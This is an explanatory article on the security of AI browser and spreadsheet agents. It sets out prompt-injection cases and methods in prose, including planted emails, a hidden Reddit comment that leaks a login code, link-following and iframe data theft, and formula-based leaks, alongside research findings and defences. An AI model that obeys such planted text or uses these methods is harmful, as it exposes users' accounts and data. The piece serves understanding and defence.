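# AI agents that operate browsers and spreadsheets: the risks of acting across tabs and files, and how their permissions are limited

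## What can an AI agent see and do in a browser or a spreadsheet?

An AI agent is a language model connected to software that carries out the actions the model proposes. A browser agent reads web pages and clicks, types and moves between sites for its user. A spreadsheet agent reads and edits a workbook's cells, formulas and sometimes scripts. Anthropic, Google, Microsoft and OpenAI offer AI tools for both browsers and spreadsheets. People mostly use them for routine tasks, such as comparing hotels across a dozen tabs, copying figures out of a supplier's portal, or finding out why one cell in a budget shows an error.

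Security researchers are interested in these agents because nearly all of them work with the user's own accounts and files while also reading text that strangers wrote. A sentence in an email or an imported table can therefore steer a program that has access to someone's bank account. In response, developers limit which sites and files an agent may use and which actions it may take without asking, and they run separate checks outside the model. How much each limit helps depends on what the agent could reach without it.

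### One cycle of a browser agent

Suppose a user has a dental clinic's booking page open and asks an agent to move Tuesday's appointment to Thursday. The model takes in text and images and puts out text. The software around it does everything else, including interacting with the browser.

The software first captures the page. It may use the text, a screenshot, the DOM (the tree of headings, buttons and form fields that the browser builds from the site's code), or a combination of these. It sends the capture to the model with the user's request and a record of the steps so far. The model responds with a tool call, a short structured message that specifies an action, in this case clicking the button labelled "Reschedule". The software performs the click, the clinic's site loads a calendar, and the software captures that page and returns it to the model as the tool result. The model then proposes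 a click on Thursday. The loop continues until the model replies to the user instead of making another tool call.

Claude in Chrome, an extension that connects Anthropic's Claude models to Google's browser, works through this exchange of calls and results, according to Anthropic's *Claude in Chrome is generally available*. The permissions that a user grants at installation give a fair idea of what the extension can do. Anthropic's *Get started with Claude in Chrome* lists one for reading page text and another, called "debugger", for clicking, typing and taking screenshots. Others let the extension open and close tabs, download files, start tasks on a schedule and detect the screen size so that it clicks in the right place.

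All the captured material accumulates in the model's context, the running text the model works from. OpenAI has a similar extension for Codex, its agent for coding and computer tasks. OpenAI's *Codex Chrome extension* lists page text, screenshots, tool calls, summaries and messages among the things that can enter that context. The clinic's page and the user's request are in the same context. Labels mark the source of each piece of text, but the model has to learn to respect them, and nothing forces it to.

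A single task may take many cycles, and the user doesn't have to watch them. Claude in Chrome keeps working after the user switches tabs, and it can repeat a saved task every day or every week. Auto browse is the agent mode of Google's Gemini assistant in Chrome. According to Google's *Ask Gemini in Chrome to complete tasks for you with auto browse*, it shows a plan and begins once the user clicks to start. It then works in its own tab until it needs the user for a step.

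### One cycle of a spreadsheet agent

Spreadsheet agents are often add-ins, third-party software that runs inside the spreadsheet program with permissions the user has granted. In Claude for Excel, for example, the user types requests in a panel beside the grid. Microsoft and Google also build their own assistants into Excel and Sheets.

Suppose an analyst asks a spreadsheet add-in to raise a growth assumption by two percentage points and report the effect on a company's valuation. The add-in first reads the workbook. Claude for Excel, for example, reads the cells, formulas and tab structure of the open workbook, according to Anthropic's *Claude for Excel*. The model receives the relevant contents and proposes an edit, such as entering 7% in cell B4 of the "Inputs" sheet. The add-in writes the value, Excel recalculates every cell that depends on it, and the model receives the new figures.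 The model then proposes another edit or reports the result.

A spreadsheet can keep recalculating an agent's formulas after the agent has finished, which has no close counterpart in the browser cycle. Most formulas only do arithmetic on other cells, but some fetch things from the internet. IMAGE loads a picture from a web address, and WEBSERVICE in Excel and IMPORTDATA in Google Sheets request data from one. An agent allowed to write any formula can therefore cause network traffic without opening a browser.

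Scripts can automate work that formulas cannot. Excel has Office Scripts, and Google Sheets has Apps Script. These scripts run with the user's identity and in some cases can call services outside the document, as PromptArmor's *AI in Excel and Google Sheets* points out. PromptArmor sells monitoring of AI vendors, so it has a commercial reason to find the problem large, though anyone can check what the functions do. Products differ in how much scripting they support. The first release of Claude for Excel could not handle macros, Excel's older kind of script, and OpenAI warns that macros may not fully work with its own add-in.

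That add-in, ChatGPT for Excel and Google Sheets, can also reach beyond the workbook through connectors, which are links that let an agent read from or act in another service, such as email or cloud storage. According to OpenAI's *ChatGPT for Excel and Google Sheets*, the add-in can search the web for material to put into the workbook and use apps that the user has connected to ChatGPT. Its listing on the Google Workspace Marketplace names Gmail, the payments company Stripe and Microsoft's document store SharePoint. If the user has connected Gmail, an agent working in a spreadsheet may therefore be able to read their email.

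### What a login hands over

When someone logs in to a website, the site gives the browser a cookie, a small piece of data that the browser sends back with later requests. The site checks the cookie from then on, so whoever operates that browser while the session lasts can do most of what the account holder can do.

An agent in the user's own browser sends its clicks with the user's cookies, so a bank receives a request that looks like an ordinary one from the customer. Google states that auto browse can access the same sites as the user, including signed-in ones. It also tells users that they are responsible for what Gemini does during a task, including mistaken purchases.

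The password manager 1Password can fill in logins for Claude in Chrome without the model receiving them, and Google Password Manager does the same for Gemini. This protects the password but does much less to protect the account, because the agent can still act on the account through the logged-in session.

Browsers have long used a rule called the same-origin policy to stop one site from interfering with another. An origin is the scheme, host and port that identify where web content comes from, so https://bank.example and https://recipes.example are different origins. (URLs usually omit the port.) Under the policy, a script on the recipe page cannot read the bank page in the next tab. The policy also applies within a single tab. An iframe is a page embedded in another page, such as an advertisement in a news article. If the advertisement comes from a different origin, its scripts cannot read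 the article.

The same-origin policy restricts scripts, but a user can still read a balance in one tab and type it into a form in another. A browser agent works from the user's side of the screen, so it can also carry text between tabs if it has access to both. A screenshot of a news article combines the article and an advertisement in one image, without showing which parts came from which origin. Products differ in how much of the separation between origins they restore.

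An agent's permission scope is the set of sites, files and actions it is allowed to use. A user might let an agent work only on a clinic's site, for example. The scope can have layers. When a user installs OpenAI's Codex extension, Chrome may ask them to let it read and change all data on all websites. OpenAI's software then narrows this by asking before the agent uses each new host, such as example.com. The extension still has the broad permission, so the narrower limit holds only as long as OpenAI's code enforces it correctly.

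### Where the browser runs

An agent built into the browser has access to a lot of context. Copilot in Microsoft Edge can read every open tab and draw on browsing history and past chats, each with the user's permission, according to Microsoft's *New updates to Edge across desktop and mobile* (2026). Gemini in Chrome can work across up to ten open tabs and connects to Gmail, Calendar and Drive, according to Google's *Get started with Gemini in Chrome*.

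An extension is separate software that the user adds to a browser, and it can access nearly as much. The Codex extension works in the user's existing Chrome profile, with its sessions and open tabs. It can also request browsing history, but the user must approve each request because OpenAI offers no way to allow access to history permanently.

OpenAI's *Using cloud browser in ChatGPT* describes a browser that runs on the company's servers. It keeps its own cookies and has no access to the user's tabs, history, saved passwords or existing logins. It keeps working on a task after the user has shut down the computer. If the task needs an account, the user signs in through a special form, and that login persists for later tasks until it expires or the user clears it.

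OpenAI and Anthropic also offer a middle option, a separate browser inside their desktop apps. It runs on the user's machine but keeps its own state. OpenAI's *Using the built-in browser in the ChatGPT desktop app* contrasts this with the extension, which uses the signed-in Chrome profile. Anthropic's *Use the built-in browser in Claude Cowork* explains that users can import cookies from their everyday browser when they first open the new one. Every site on the import list is selected by default, with banking and email sites labelled and placed at the top. Users who accept the default give the separate browser much the same authority as their everyday one, and Claude can use those logins in later sessions on that computer.

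Where an agent browses can also change partway through a task. Since July 2026, Gemini Spark, another of Google's agents, has been able to use Chrome with the user's logged-in accounts (Coimbra and Dsilva, 2026, *Gemini Spark now integrates with Chrome*). If the user's computer turns off before Spark has finished, Spark may continue in a remote browser. It may do the same after the user presses Stop in Chrome's side panel, because that button ends only the browsing, and cancelling the task takes a separate click. A separate or remote browser does protect the user at first, but how long that protection lasts depends on how many logins the user adds.

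### What a data thief needs

Prompt injection is text in material the agent reads that the model treats as an instruction. In the cases relevant here, a third party has planted the text. Anthropic gives the example of a user who asks for draft replies to some emails, one of which contains a hidden instruction to forward the user's other emails to the attacker. If the agent complies, it sends private data to someone who should not have it, which is called exfiltration.

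Simon Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, reduced this kind of theft to three conditions. Willison is a software developer who has followed prompt injection closely on his weblog, and his claim is that an attacker can steal data from an agent that combines

- access to private data,
- exposure to untrusted content, and
- some way to communicate with the outside.

A browser agent in a logged-in inbox meets all three conditions on a single site, because the mail is private, anyone can send a message to the inbox, and the agent can send messages out. Elsewhere on the web, the conditions are spread over several sites but are no harder to meet. OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) lists attachments, calendar invitations, shared documents, forums and social media posts among the places where an agent may encounter hostile text.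 The agent can then send data out through a form or a message. It can also do so merely by opening a page, because a web address can contain data and the receiving server can record it.

Spreadsheets are often less safe than they look, because the owner may have written only part of the workbook. PromptArmor lists market data pasted from websites, questionnaires filled in by vendors, exports from customer databases with free-text fields, and integrations that turn incoming emails into rows. The private data may be elsewhere in the same workbook, such as salaries or an unpublished forecast. It can leak through scripts, web searches and formulas that fetch from the web. When Anthropic tested the first release of Claude for Excel, it found edge cases in which someone could manipulate the tool into leaking sensitive information through formulas, search queries or access to files. It advised customers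 to use the tool only with spreadsheets they trusted.

The exceptions are also the cases in which the agent is least useful. A remote browser with no logins or connected apps holds little worth stealing, and a workbook its owner typed from scratch contains no text from strangers until the agent searches the web.

Willison and OpenAI disagree, at least in practice, about whether to remove one of the three conditions. Willison argues in *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”* that removing one is the only reliable defence, and that the agent's ability to send data out is generally the easiest to remove. By his standard, a defence that stops 99% of attacks fails, because attackers will look for the remaining 1%. OpenAI lets the agent keep its abilities and tries to make attacks rarer and harder to carry out. It doubts that prompt injection will ever be fully solved and says firm guarantees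 are hard to achieve.

Willison has the stronger argument about what would count as a guarantee, but his remedy is harder to apply than it sounds, as a case he reported in July 2026 shows. Anthropic had restricted the page-fetching tool in its Claude chat product so that the model could not compose its own web addresses and could open only those that the user had typed, that a search had returned, or that appeared on pages it had already fetched. A researcher, Ayush Paul, built a site of nested links, one for each letter of the alphabet, and induced the model to spell out the user's name by choosing which links to follow. He also obtained the user's home city and employer. Anthropic closed the gap by removing the tool's ability to follow links from fetched pages. That fix is workable for a chat assistant, but a browser agent that cannot follow links would lose most of its usefulness.

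The three conditions cover only data theft. An agent can also do damage when it cannot send data out. In testing Claude for Excel, Anthropic also found that the agent could be manipulated into altering financial records or deleting data across several sheets. An attacker needs only hostile text and an agent with permission to edit to do this.

### The main products in late 2026

Several products named in older security research have since been withdrawn or renamed. OpenAI withdrew its own browser, ChatGPT Atlas, and *Evolving Atlas into ChatGPT for browser-based agentic work* gives August 9, 2026 as the date set for it to stop working. Users now have a browser inside the desktop app, a Chrome extension, and a tool that operates desktop programs, according to OpenAI's *Using your computer and browser*. Microsoft retired Copilot Mode in Edge in May 2026 and renamed its agent feature Browse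 with Copilot. The same month, it opened a limited preview of agentic browsing for companies, according to Microsoft's *New in Edge for Business* (2026). Google brought auto browse to Android phones in the United States in August, according to Dsilva's *Tap into the power of Gemini in Chrome on Android* (2026).

ChatGPT's spreadsheet add-in was first released in beta in March 2026 and became generally available in May, according to OpenAI's *Introducing ChatGPT for Excel and new financial data integrations* (2026). Copilot in Excel now has an Agent Mode that edits workbooks in several steps, and Microsoft's *Agent Mode in Excel* (2025) lists it as launched worldwide. According to PromptArmor, Gemini in Sheets mostly generates tables, summarises data and suggests formulas, so its range of actions is narrower than that of the other two.

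| Product | Where the agent sits | Availability | Source |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude in Chrome | Extension in the user's Chrome | All paid Claude plans; no mobile version | Anthropic |
| ChatGPT Atlas | OpenAI's own browser | Withdrawn; end date August 9, 2026 | OpenAI |
| ChatGPT cloud browser | OpenAI's servers | Paid plans except Go, in supported regions | OpenAI |
| Gemini in Chrome (auto browse) | Built into Chrome | Gradual release; 20 tasks a day on AI Pro, 200 on AI Ultra | Google |
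| Comet | Perplexity's own browser | In use by October 2025, when the rival browser maker Brave published an attack on it | Willison |
| Copilot in Edge (Browse with Copilot) | Built into Edge | Microsoft 365 Premium subscribers in the US, desktop only | Microsoft |
| Claude for Excel | Add-in | Limited beta in late 2025; among the tools PromptArmor reviewed in May 2026 | PromptArmor |
| ChatGPT for Excel and Google Sheets | Add-in | All ChatGPT plans, including Free | OpenAI |
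| Copilot in Excel (Agent Mode) | Built into Excel | Microsoft 365 subscribers, on web, Windows and Mac | Microsoft |
| Gemini in Sheets | Built into Google Sheets | Among the tools PromptArmor reviewed in May 2026 | PromptArmor |

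## How can text on a web page take control of a browser agent?

A browser agent's model receives the user's request and the text of a web page in one stream, and it cannot reliably tell which parts are commands. If someone plants an instruction on the page, the agent may carry it out using the user's logins. Training makes this much rarer. By mid-2026, the best models ignored nearly every planted instruction in their developers' tests, but nobody can show that they will always do so.

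### One stream of text

Database software has long had a similar problem. Many websites insert what a visitor types into a form into a command in SQL, a language for querying databases. In an SQL injection attack, the visitor types something that the database runs as part of the command. Programmers can prevent this with parameterised queries, which send the command and the visitor's text to the database separately, so that the database never runs the text.

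David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC), argued in December 2025 in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* that language models have no built-in separation between instructions and data. A model works on tokens, which are words or pieces of words, and predicts each next token from all the tokens before it. Tokens from a web page go through the same calculation as tokens from the user, and so do the labels that mark where each piece of text came from.

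In security, a "confused deputy" is a program that someone with fewer privileges tricks into using its greater privileges on their behalf. Programmers can normally fix this flaw, but David C calls language models "inherently confusable" and doubts that developers can ever rule out the confusion. He therefore advises developers to limit what a confused model can do, and suggests that a language model may be a poor choice for a system that can't tolerate the remaining risk.

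Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026), in *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, looked for this confusion inside the models. They wrapped each passage of ordinary web text in five different labels in turn, including those for the user's messages, the model's own reasoning and the output of tools. They then trained a simple classifier, called a probe, to identify the label from the model's internal activity. Since the text was the same under every label, the probe could learn only the effect of the label.

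The researchers applied the probe to a short conversation about gardening. With the correct labels in place, it assigned the model's reasoning an average 85% probability of being reasoning. The average was 83% with all labels removed, and still 85% when the researchers labelled the whole conversation as the user's text. The style of the text had much the same internal effect as the label, and had the stronger effect when the two conflicted.

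A browser agent can therefore treat a sentence on a page as the user's because it is phrased like a user's request, even though it arrives labelled as tool output. Ye and colleagues tested whether this confusion is linked to behaviour in 1,000 attempts to make an agent leak data. The attack succeeded in 2% of attempts in the group where the probe measured the least confusion about the source, and in 70% where it measured the most. In a separate experiment, they reworded planted text so that it kept its argument but lost the style of the source it imitated, and the success rate fell from 61% to 10%, so the link is unlikely to be a coincidence. The probes need access to a model's internals, so outsiders can't repeat the measurement on most of the commercial models that run browser agents.

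### What training changes

Ye and colleagues distinguish two ways a model can resist a planted instruction. It can identify the text as coming from a web page and ignore any command in it, however the attacker phrases it. Or it can recognise the command because it resembles attacks from training, which gives much less protection against an unfamiliar attack. They argue that current models rely mainly on the second method. Their evidence is that skilled human testers and attackers who adapt to the defence often succeed against models with nearly perfect scores on standard tests.

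Anthropic said in November 2025 that it trains its model to resist planted instructions by putting them into simulated web pages and rewarding the model when it identifies them and refuses to comply. When a new attack succeeds against a current model, Anthropic adds it to a library that it uses to train later ones. OpenAI similarly trains its models on attacks that an automated attacker finds. Each round of training makes a successful attack harder to find, but the model still receives the user's commands and the page's text in one stream, so the developer can't prove that no working attack is left. Filters can't rule out every attack either. David C warns against relying on lists of forbidden phrases, since an attacker can reword an instruction in endless ways.

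Developers cannot train an agent to ignore every instruction it reads on a page, because some tasks depend on those instructions. A user who asks the agent to complete a visa application wants it to follow the form's note about date formats, and a user who asks it to follow a setup guide has authorized it to carry out the guide's instructions. The agent has to judge which instructions serve the user's request, and an attacker can write an instruction that appears to serve it.

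### How hostile text reaches the agent

An attacker has to get text in front of the agent, and the web offers many ways to do it.

- The operator of a website can put instructions in its own pages. Khodayari, Acharya, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, traced about 80% of the planted instructions they found on the public web to the site's operator.
- People can post text on sites they don't control. Job listings and other material from third parties accounted for about 20% of the instructions in the same survey. Comments and similar contributions from users made up only 1.4%, although the survey largely missed social media.
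- Advertisers supply material that other sites embed in iframes, and its words can enter the agent's context with the rest of the page. Anthropic counts advertisements, embedded documents and scripts that load after the page among the possible routes.
- Anyone who knows a person's address can send them an email or a calendar invitation.
- A collaborator can hide text in a shared document. Soon after OpenAI launched Atlas in October 2025, researchers redirected its agent with a few words in a Google Doc, according to Nolan (2025), in *OpenAI says prompt injections that can trick AI browsers like ChatGPT Atlas*.
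- A link can lead the agent to a hostile page, and the web address can itself contain an instruction. So can the title of a browser tab, as Anthropic's *Piloting Claude for Chrome* notes.

The user often can't see the text. Khodayari and colleagues classed 87% of the instructions in their survey as invisible to a person viewing the page. Site operators and others had put them in comments in the page's code, matched the text colour to the background, or made the letters tiny. Just over half were in HTTP headers, information that a server sends along with a page. An agent that works from screenshots would miss those, while one that reads the page's code may take in form fields and comments that its user never sees.

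Khodayari and colleagues also tested how the format of a captured page affects the model. In 5,200 runs, they asked 13 models to summarize 100 pages containing planted instructions, with each page supplied in four formats. The models followed the planted instruction in 3.9% of runs when they received plain text, and in 1.1% when they received either the page's code or a structured snapshot of it. Plain text removes the clues that the instruction was hidden. The rate for page code is artificially low, however, because about a fifth of those runs ended in errors, mostly on pages too long for the model. In six runs, a model identified the planted instruction as suspicious but still followed it.

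### Two planted emails and a Reddit comment

In December 2025, OpenAI described an attack on Atlas that its automated attacker had found. The attacker placed an email in the user's inbox containing an instruction to send a resignation letter to the user's chief executive. Later, the user asked the agent to draft an out-of-office reply. While working on this, the agent read the planted email, which added the email's text to the model's context alongside the user's request. The model treated that text as an instruction to follow, so the agent sent the resignation letter and never wrote the out-of-office reply.

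The agent read and sent mail, as it ordinarily would in an inbox, but it followed the attacker's instruction instead of the user's. The attack needed no stolen password or flaw in the mail site. The user had also been quite careful, since asking for an out-of-office reply is about as narrow as a request can be. OpenAI advises people to avoid broad requests, such as telling the agent to review their email and take whatever action is needed, because they make it easier for hidden text to influence the agent. It says narrow requests reduce the risk but don't eliminate it. OpenAI also trained a new version of the model against attacks from its automated attacker and released it to all Atlas users.

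Anthropic had found a similar weakness in its own extension by August 2025. Its testers posed as the user's employer in an email, asked for messages to be deleted for "mailbox hygiene", and claimed that no further confirmation was necessary. When Claude processed the inbox, it deleted the user's emails without asking. After Anthropic added new defences, Claude identified the same email as a likely phishing attempt and left the mailbox alone.

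Brave published its finding on Comet, Perplexity's browser, in the same month. Brave makes a rival browser and was developing its own agent, so it had a commercial interest in the finding. In *Agentic Browser Security*, Chaikin and Sahib describe a demonstration in which they hid an instruction in a Reddit comment. When a user clicked Comet's button to summarise the page, the agent collected the user's email address and a one-time login code from their Gmail, then posted both as a reply on Reddit. The attacker could use them to take over the user's Perplexity account.

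Chaikin and Sahib found that Comet passed part of the page to its model without distinguishing it from the user's instructions, so it lacked even the imperfect protection of labels. They recommended separating page content from the user's instructions, but said developers should still treat the model's output as unsafe.

The repair took several attempts. Brave reported the problem on July 25, 2025, and Perplexity made a first fix two days later, which Brave found incomplete. A test on August 13 suggested that the attack no longer worked, but after publishing its account on August 20, Brave discovered that Perplexity still hadn't fully blocked attacks of this kind. Perplexity also had an earlier warning from the security firm Trail of Bits, which it hired to test Comet before launch. The firm showed that four prompt injection techniques could extract private information from a user's Gmail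 (*Using threat modeling and prompt injection to audit Comet*, 2026).

In June 2026, the security firm LayerX reported that, in a harmless test, it had tricked six AI browsers and extensions, including Atlas, Comet and Anthropic's extension, into sending login credentials to an attacker (Mascellino, 2026, *Researchers Trick AI Browsers Into Leaking Credentials*). LayerX said that OpenAI fixed the problem, Perplexity closed the report without acting, Anthropic tried a fix that failed, and the smaller makers Fellou, Genspark and Sigma did not reply.

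### Is the problem close to solved?

OpenAI wrote in December 2025 that prompt injection is "unlikely to ever be fully 'solved'" and compared it to scams aimed at people. David C reached much the same conclusion that month, based on how models process text. Gavish (2026) of Google wrote in April that developers can't solve it once and move on, in *Google Workspace’s continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections*. Charlie Eriksen, a researcher at Aikido Security, told Nolan that conventional browsers treat the web as untrusted, whereas an agent lets web content influence its actions. He expects prompt injection to remain a long-term problem.

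The Decoder was more optimistic about Anthropic's Claude Opus 5 in a mid-2026 article titled *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*. In 129 browser test scenarios, no attack succeeded when Anthropic's added safeguards were on, though some did when they were off. The safeguards scan incoming text for hidden instructions and check the agent's actions before they run, so the result reflects the model and the safeguards together.

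Anthropic's own claims are more modest than the headline. It retired an older test because its newest models no longer failed it, but some attacks in the harder replacement still succeeded against the models when they ran without safeguards. Anthropic calls prompt injection "a moving target" and still describes it on a help page as the biggest risk for AI tools that use a browser.

The two sides partly address different questions. David C's argument shows that a language model offers no guarantee, but it doesn't establish how rare successful attacks can become. Anthropic's tests show that the attacks its testers know about now rarely succeed. The tests can't show what a determined outsider would find next, so outside research on current products is especially valuable.

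In August 2026, the cybersecurity firm Zenity presented more than 20 security issues across browser agents from Anthropic, Google, Microsoft, OpenAI and Perplexity, according to Gulf News' *WhatsApp warning*. SC Media's *Agentic anarchy* reports that Google patched every flaw Zenity raised. The other makers said they could not reproduce some of the flaws, already knew about them or did not consider them worth fixing. SC Media favours Gemini in Chrome, while Gulf News says Atlas did best.

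Zenity's work is good evidence that released products were vulnerable, but weaker evidence that the newest models are. Zenity sent its findings to OpenAI in January 2026, months before Opus 5 came out, and OpenAI said it had strengthened Atlas since. Still, a good result on the developer's own tests doesn't justify calling the problem "solved", especially when the developer had to replace the previous test within about a year. Defenses have improved, though, and an attack that would have worked in 2025 with one plausible email now often has to get past a better-trained model and two separate checks.

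### Attacks outside the laboratory

People plant instructions for AI systems on the public web, though rarely to steal from anyone. Khodayari and colleagues searched 1.2 billion web addresses, mostly from an October 2025 crawl by Common Crawl, a public archive of web pages. They added results from two search engines for internet-connected machines. They confirmed about 15,400 planted instructions on 11,700 pages. Within Common Crawl, roughly one address in 124,000 contained planted instructions.

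The largest group, with 8,894 instructions, was meant to disrupt AI systems, usually by making them produce nonsense. Another 4,093 were meant to stop AI systems from reusing personal or copyrighted material, 3,096 to expose automated visitors, and 1,521 to promote a product, source or person. Some instructions had more than one purpose. Only 13 were meant to extract data. Nine of those requested the developer's instructions to the model, and four requested other secrets.

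Most of these instructions targeted crawlers and other tools that collect web content in bulk. About two-thirds of the affected pages with an archived copy from a year earlier already contained a planted instruction then, so many of the instructions can't have been written for Atlas, which OpenAI released only in October 2025. The survey probably undercounts, since it searched for known phrases and could miss disguised or non-English text.

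Google reported similar results in April 2026 from its own scans of Common Crawl. It mostly found pranks, attempts to promote a business, and instructions to AI systems to stay away. It also found a few unsophisticated attempts to steal data and some file-deletion commands that it thought were unlikely to work. The malicious category grew by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026, but Google published no counts, so the increase may be from a very small base.

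Other researchers found clearer attempts to make money. The security company Forcepoint found a page with instructions for a complete PayPal payment, aimed at agents able to pay, according to Help Net Security's *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild* (2026). Another page was written to steer payments to a donation link. Neither Google nor Forcepoint found a sophisticated, coordinated campaign, though Forcepoint saw the same templates on several sites and suspected that their creators were sharing tools. Zscaler, another security company, found two campaigns that pushed hostile sites up the search results so that agents would find them. One used fake software documentation for a payment scam, and the other impersonated a cryptocurrency service, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents*. Unit 42, the threat research team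 at Palo Alto Networks, found an attempt to get past an AI system that reviews advertisements.

There is very little documented harm to real users. The resignation letter, the deleted mailbox and the Comet account takeover all come from tests, as do the findings by LayerX and Zenity. The large scans counted planted text, and neither Khodayari and colleagues nor Google identified anyone who lost money or data because a web page hijacked their browser agent. The payment scams show that some attackers hope to profit, but they don't show that any agent obeyed the planted instructions.

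The low count is only mildly reassuring. A scan of the public web doesn't cover private mail, calendars or shared documents, and someone targeting a particular inbox would send it an email. Google's scan also missed most social media. Victims may not recognise an attack, because a hijacked agent acts through their account and its messages or payments can look like theirs. Google expects attempts to become more common and more sophisticated, partly because newer AI systems are more capable. Earlier ones often failed to carry out malicious actions even after an attacker had taken control of them.

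## Can one website reach another through the agent?

In some browsers, one website can reach another through the agent. The same-origin policy restricts scripts, but not an agent that reads both sites for the user. If a hostile page can get that agent to follow its instructions, the agent can fetch information that the page's own scripts can't reach. A product's exposure depends on what its agent reads, what it can do on a page, and how well the model ignores planted text.

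### How the University of Washington tested seven browsers

Roesner and Kohlbrenner (2026), security researchers at the University of Washington, compared seven browsers in late January and early February 2026. They presented their paper, *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy*, that April at a workshop of ICLR, a machine learning conference. They tested Atlas, Comet, Gemini in Chrome, Claude in Chrome, Copilot in Edge, and two more limited assistants, Leo in Brave and AI Mode in Firefox. They tested Atlas with and without Agent Mode, which lets ChatGPT operate the browser.

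The researchers built small test pages on two domains, with statements about a fictional woman named Alice. Alice likes cats on one page, horses in an iframe on that page, and koalas in a second tab. The researchers asked each agent which animals Alice likes, and an answer that included horses showed that the agent had read the iframe. Another page mentioned donkeys in an invisible part of its code and fish far below the visible area. It also mentioned pigs if the browser sent a certain cookie and cows if it didn't, and this test showed that every agent saw the page as the logged-in user would.

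The researchers also typed words into a text field and a password field, asked the agent to read them back, and then asked it to fill in the fields itself. Finally, they put instructions on a page and told the agent to follow them. This is a crude test of prompt injection, because the user has told the agent to obey the page, but the researchers only wanted to see whether an agent would act on a page's instructions at all.

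The researchers recorded a "yes" if an agent did something even once, and repeated a failed attempt at least three times in fresh chats before recording a "no". A "no" is therefore weaker evidence than a "yes". An agent may leave out an iframe because the browser never sends it to the model, or because the model receives it but doesn't use it, in which case a better-worded prompt might work. In Firefox, the cause is clearly the browser. The researchers could read the prompt Firefox writes when the user clicks a summary button, and it contained only the outer page's text. The cause is less clear for Atlas without Agent Mode, but it sometimes included iframe text in early trials and later stopped, which suggests that the limit came from the model.

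The researchers used two settings that were less cautious than the alternatives. They let Claude follow its own plans without asking for approval, and they ran Atlas's Agent Mode with the user's logins available. The makers offer both options, but a careful user might choose neither.

### What the agents read and did

The table gives the main results from Roesner and Kohlbrenner. "With permission" means that the user had to allow the access first.

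| Agent | Reads iframes from other origins | Reads tabs from other origins | Reads masked passwords | Reads hidden elements | Types into pages | Runs its own JavaScript | Uses past chats across tabs |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Leo in Brave | No | With permission | No | No | No | No | No |
| Atlas, no Agent Mode | No | Through chat memory | No | Yes | With permission | No | Yes |
| Atlas, Agent Mode | Yes | No | Yes, in logged-in mode | Yes | Yes | No | Yes |
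| Gemini in Chrome | Yes | With permission | No | No | Yes, with auto browse | No | Yes |
| Claude in Chrome | Yes | With permission | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes | No |
| Copilot in Edge | No | Yes | No | No | No | No | No |
| AI Mode in Firefox | No | No | No | No | No | No | No |
| Comet | Yes | No | No | No | Yes, except passwords | No | Yes |

The makers haven't agreed on where the boundaries between sites should be. Copilot in Edge read every open tab without a permission prompt, but did not seem to detect the iframe on the test page. Comet read iframes but not tabs from other origins. Some agents ignored all iframes, even those from the same origin, which is stricter than the same-origin policy requires.

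Claude in Chrome was the only agent that ran its own JavaScript, the programming language of web pages. It ran these scripts in the main page and inside iframes from other origins. It can do this because it is an extension with permission to access content on all domains, whereas the other agents are built into the browser. The same-origin policy treats a script running inside a page as the page's own, with the same authority.

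Claude in Chrome and Atlas in Agent Mode could also read a password that appeared on screen as dots. The dots hide the password from someone looking over the user's shoulder, but the characters are still in the page's data. Claude told the researchers it had used a tool that reads the DOM. Agents' accounts of how they work aren't very reliable, but this one is plausible because a screenshot would have shown only the dots.

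### Stealing data from another site

Roesner and Kohlbrenner describe a kind of theft in which an attacker's page uses an iframe to embed a page from a site where the user has an account.

1. The user opens the attacker's page, which loads the other site in an iframe.
2. The user asks the agent to summarise the page.
3. The agent reads both sites, along with an instruction that the attacker has planted on the outer page.
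4. The agent follows the instruction and types a summary, including text from the iframe, into a form on the attacker's page.
5. The form submits itself, and the attacker's server receives the text.

The same-origin policy allows this because the attacker's scripts read only what the agent typed into the attacker's own form, never the other site itself. The browser doesn't block any of the steps, because it treats the agent's typing much as it would treat the user's.

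The researchers made this work on Atlas in Agent Mode, using their own test pages. They also made it work in reverse, with the iframe taking text from the surrounding page.

The second direction is more worrying in practice. Many sites that hold private data refuse to load inside another site's iframe, and browsers often withhold a site's cookies when it loads there. An attacker who embeds a bank's site would therefore usually get an error or a logged-out page. These protections don't help when the hostile content is an advertisement inside the user's webmail, because the mail site has loaded normally with the user's cookies and itself embeds the advertisement.

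An attacker may be able to reach a second site through the agent without using an iframe. Trail of Bits' *Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities* (2026) describes working attacks on several products, which the firm didn't name because their makers declined to coordinate disclosure. In one attack, the user asked the agent to summarise a hostile document. The agent then loaded a second site with the user's cookies, found personal information there and sent it out in a web address. The second site didn't have to be open already, since the agent could open it. Restricting where the agent could send requests didn't reliably prevent leaks, because a search query or a failed address lookup can also carry data.

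Data can also cross between sites after the agent has left the first one. In *Same-Origin Policy for Agentic Browsers*, Wang, Chen and colleagues (2026) had agents do two ordinary tasks in a row. The first was on a page with private information, such as an insurance account. The second was on a page from a different origin, where an attacker had planted instructions to write that information into the page. The information was still in the agent's context when it began the second task. The researchers counted a leak only when the agent wrote exactly the information the attacker wanted.

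Atlas leaked in 99 of 150 runs, a total added up from the reported results. Comet leaked in 92 to 100 of 150, depending on which of three models it used. Atlas leaked in 29 of 30 runs on imitation Google Forms, where the attacker controlled the whole page, and in 12 of 30 on imitation GitHub pages, where the attacker could only post content.

Those rates are high for two released products, although the pages and private data were artificial, and the researchers ran each pairing of sites only three times per model. The researchers used a fairly basic attack on Atlas and Comet, writing the planted text by hand because testing those products took manual work. On open-source agents, they also used an adaptive attacker, a program that kept revising the text based on the agent's responses. In one pairing, this raised the share of runs with a leak from 42% to 84%, so the 66% rate for Atlas is not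 an upper limit.

### Taking actions on another site

Forging an action is often simpler than stealing data, because the attacker doesn't need to get anything back. Websites have dealt for decades with a version of this problem called cross-site request forgery, in which a hostile page makes the user's browser send a request to another site with the user's cookies attached. The other site can usually detect this by putting a secret value in its own forms and rejecting requests without it. An agent tricked by a hostile page gets past that defence because it opens and submits the genuine form, which contains the secret value.

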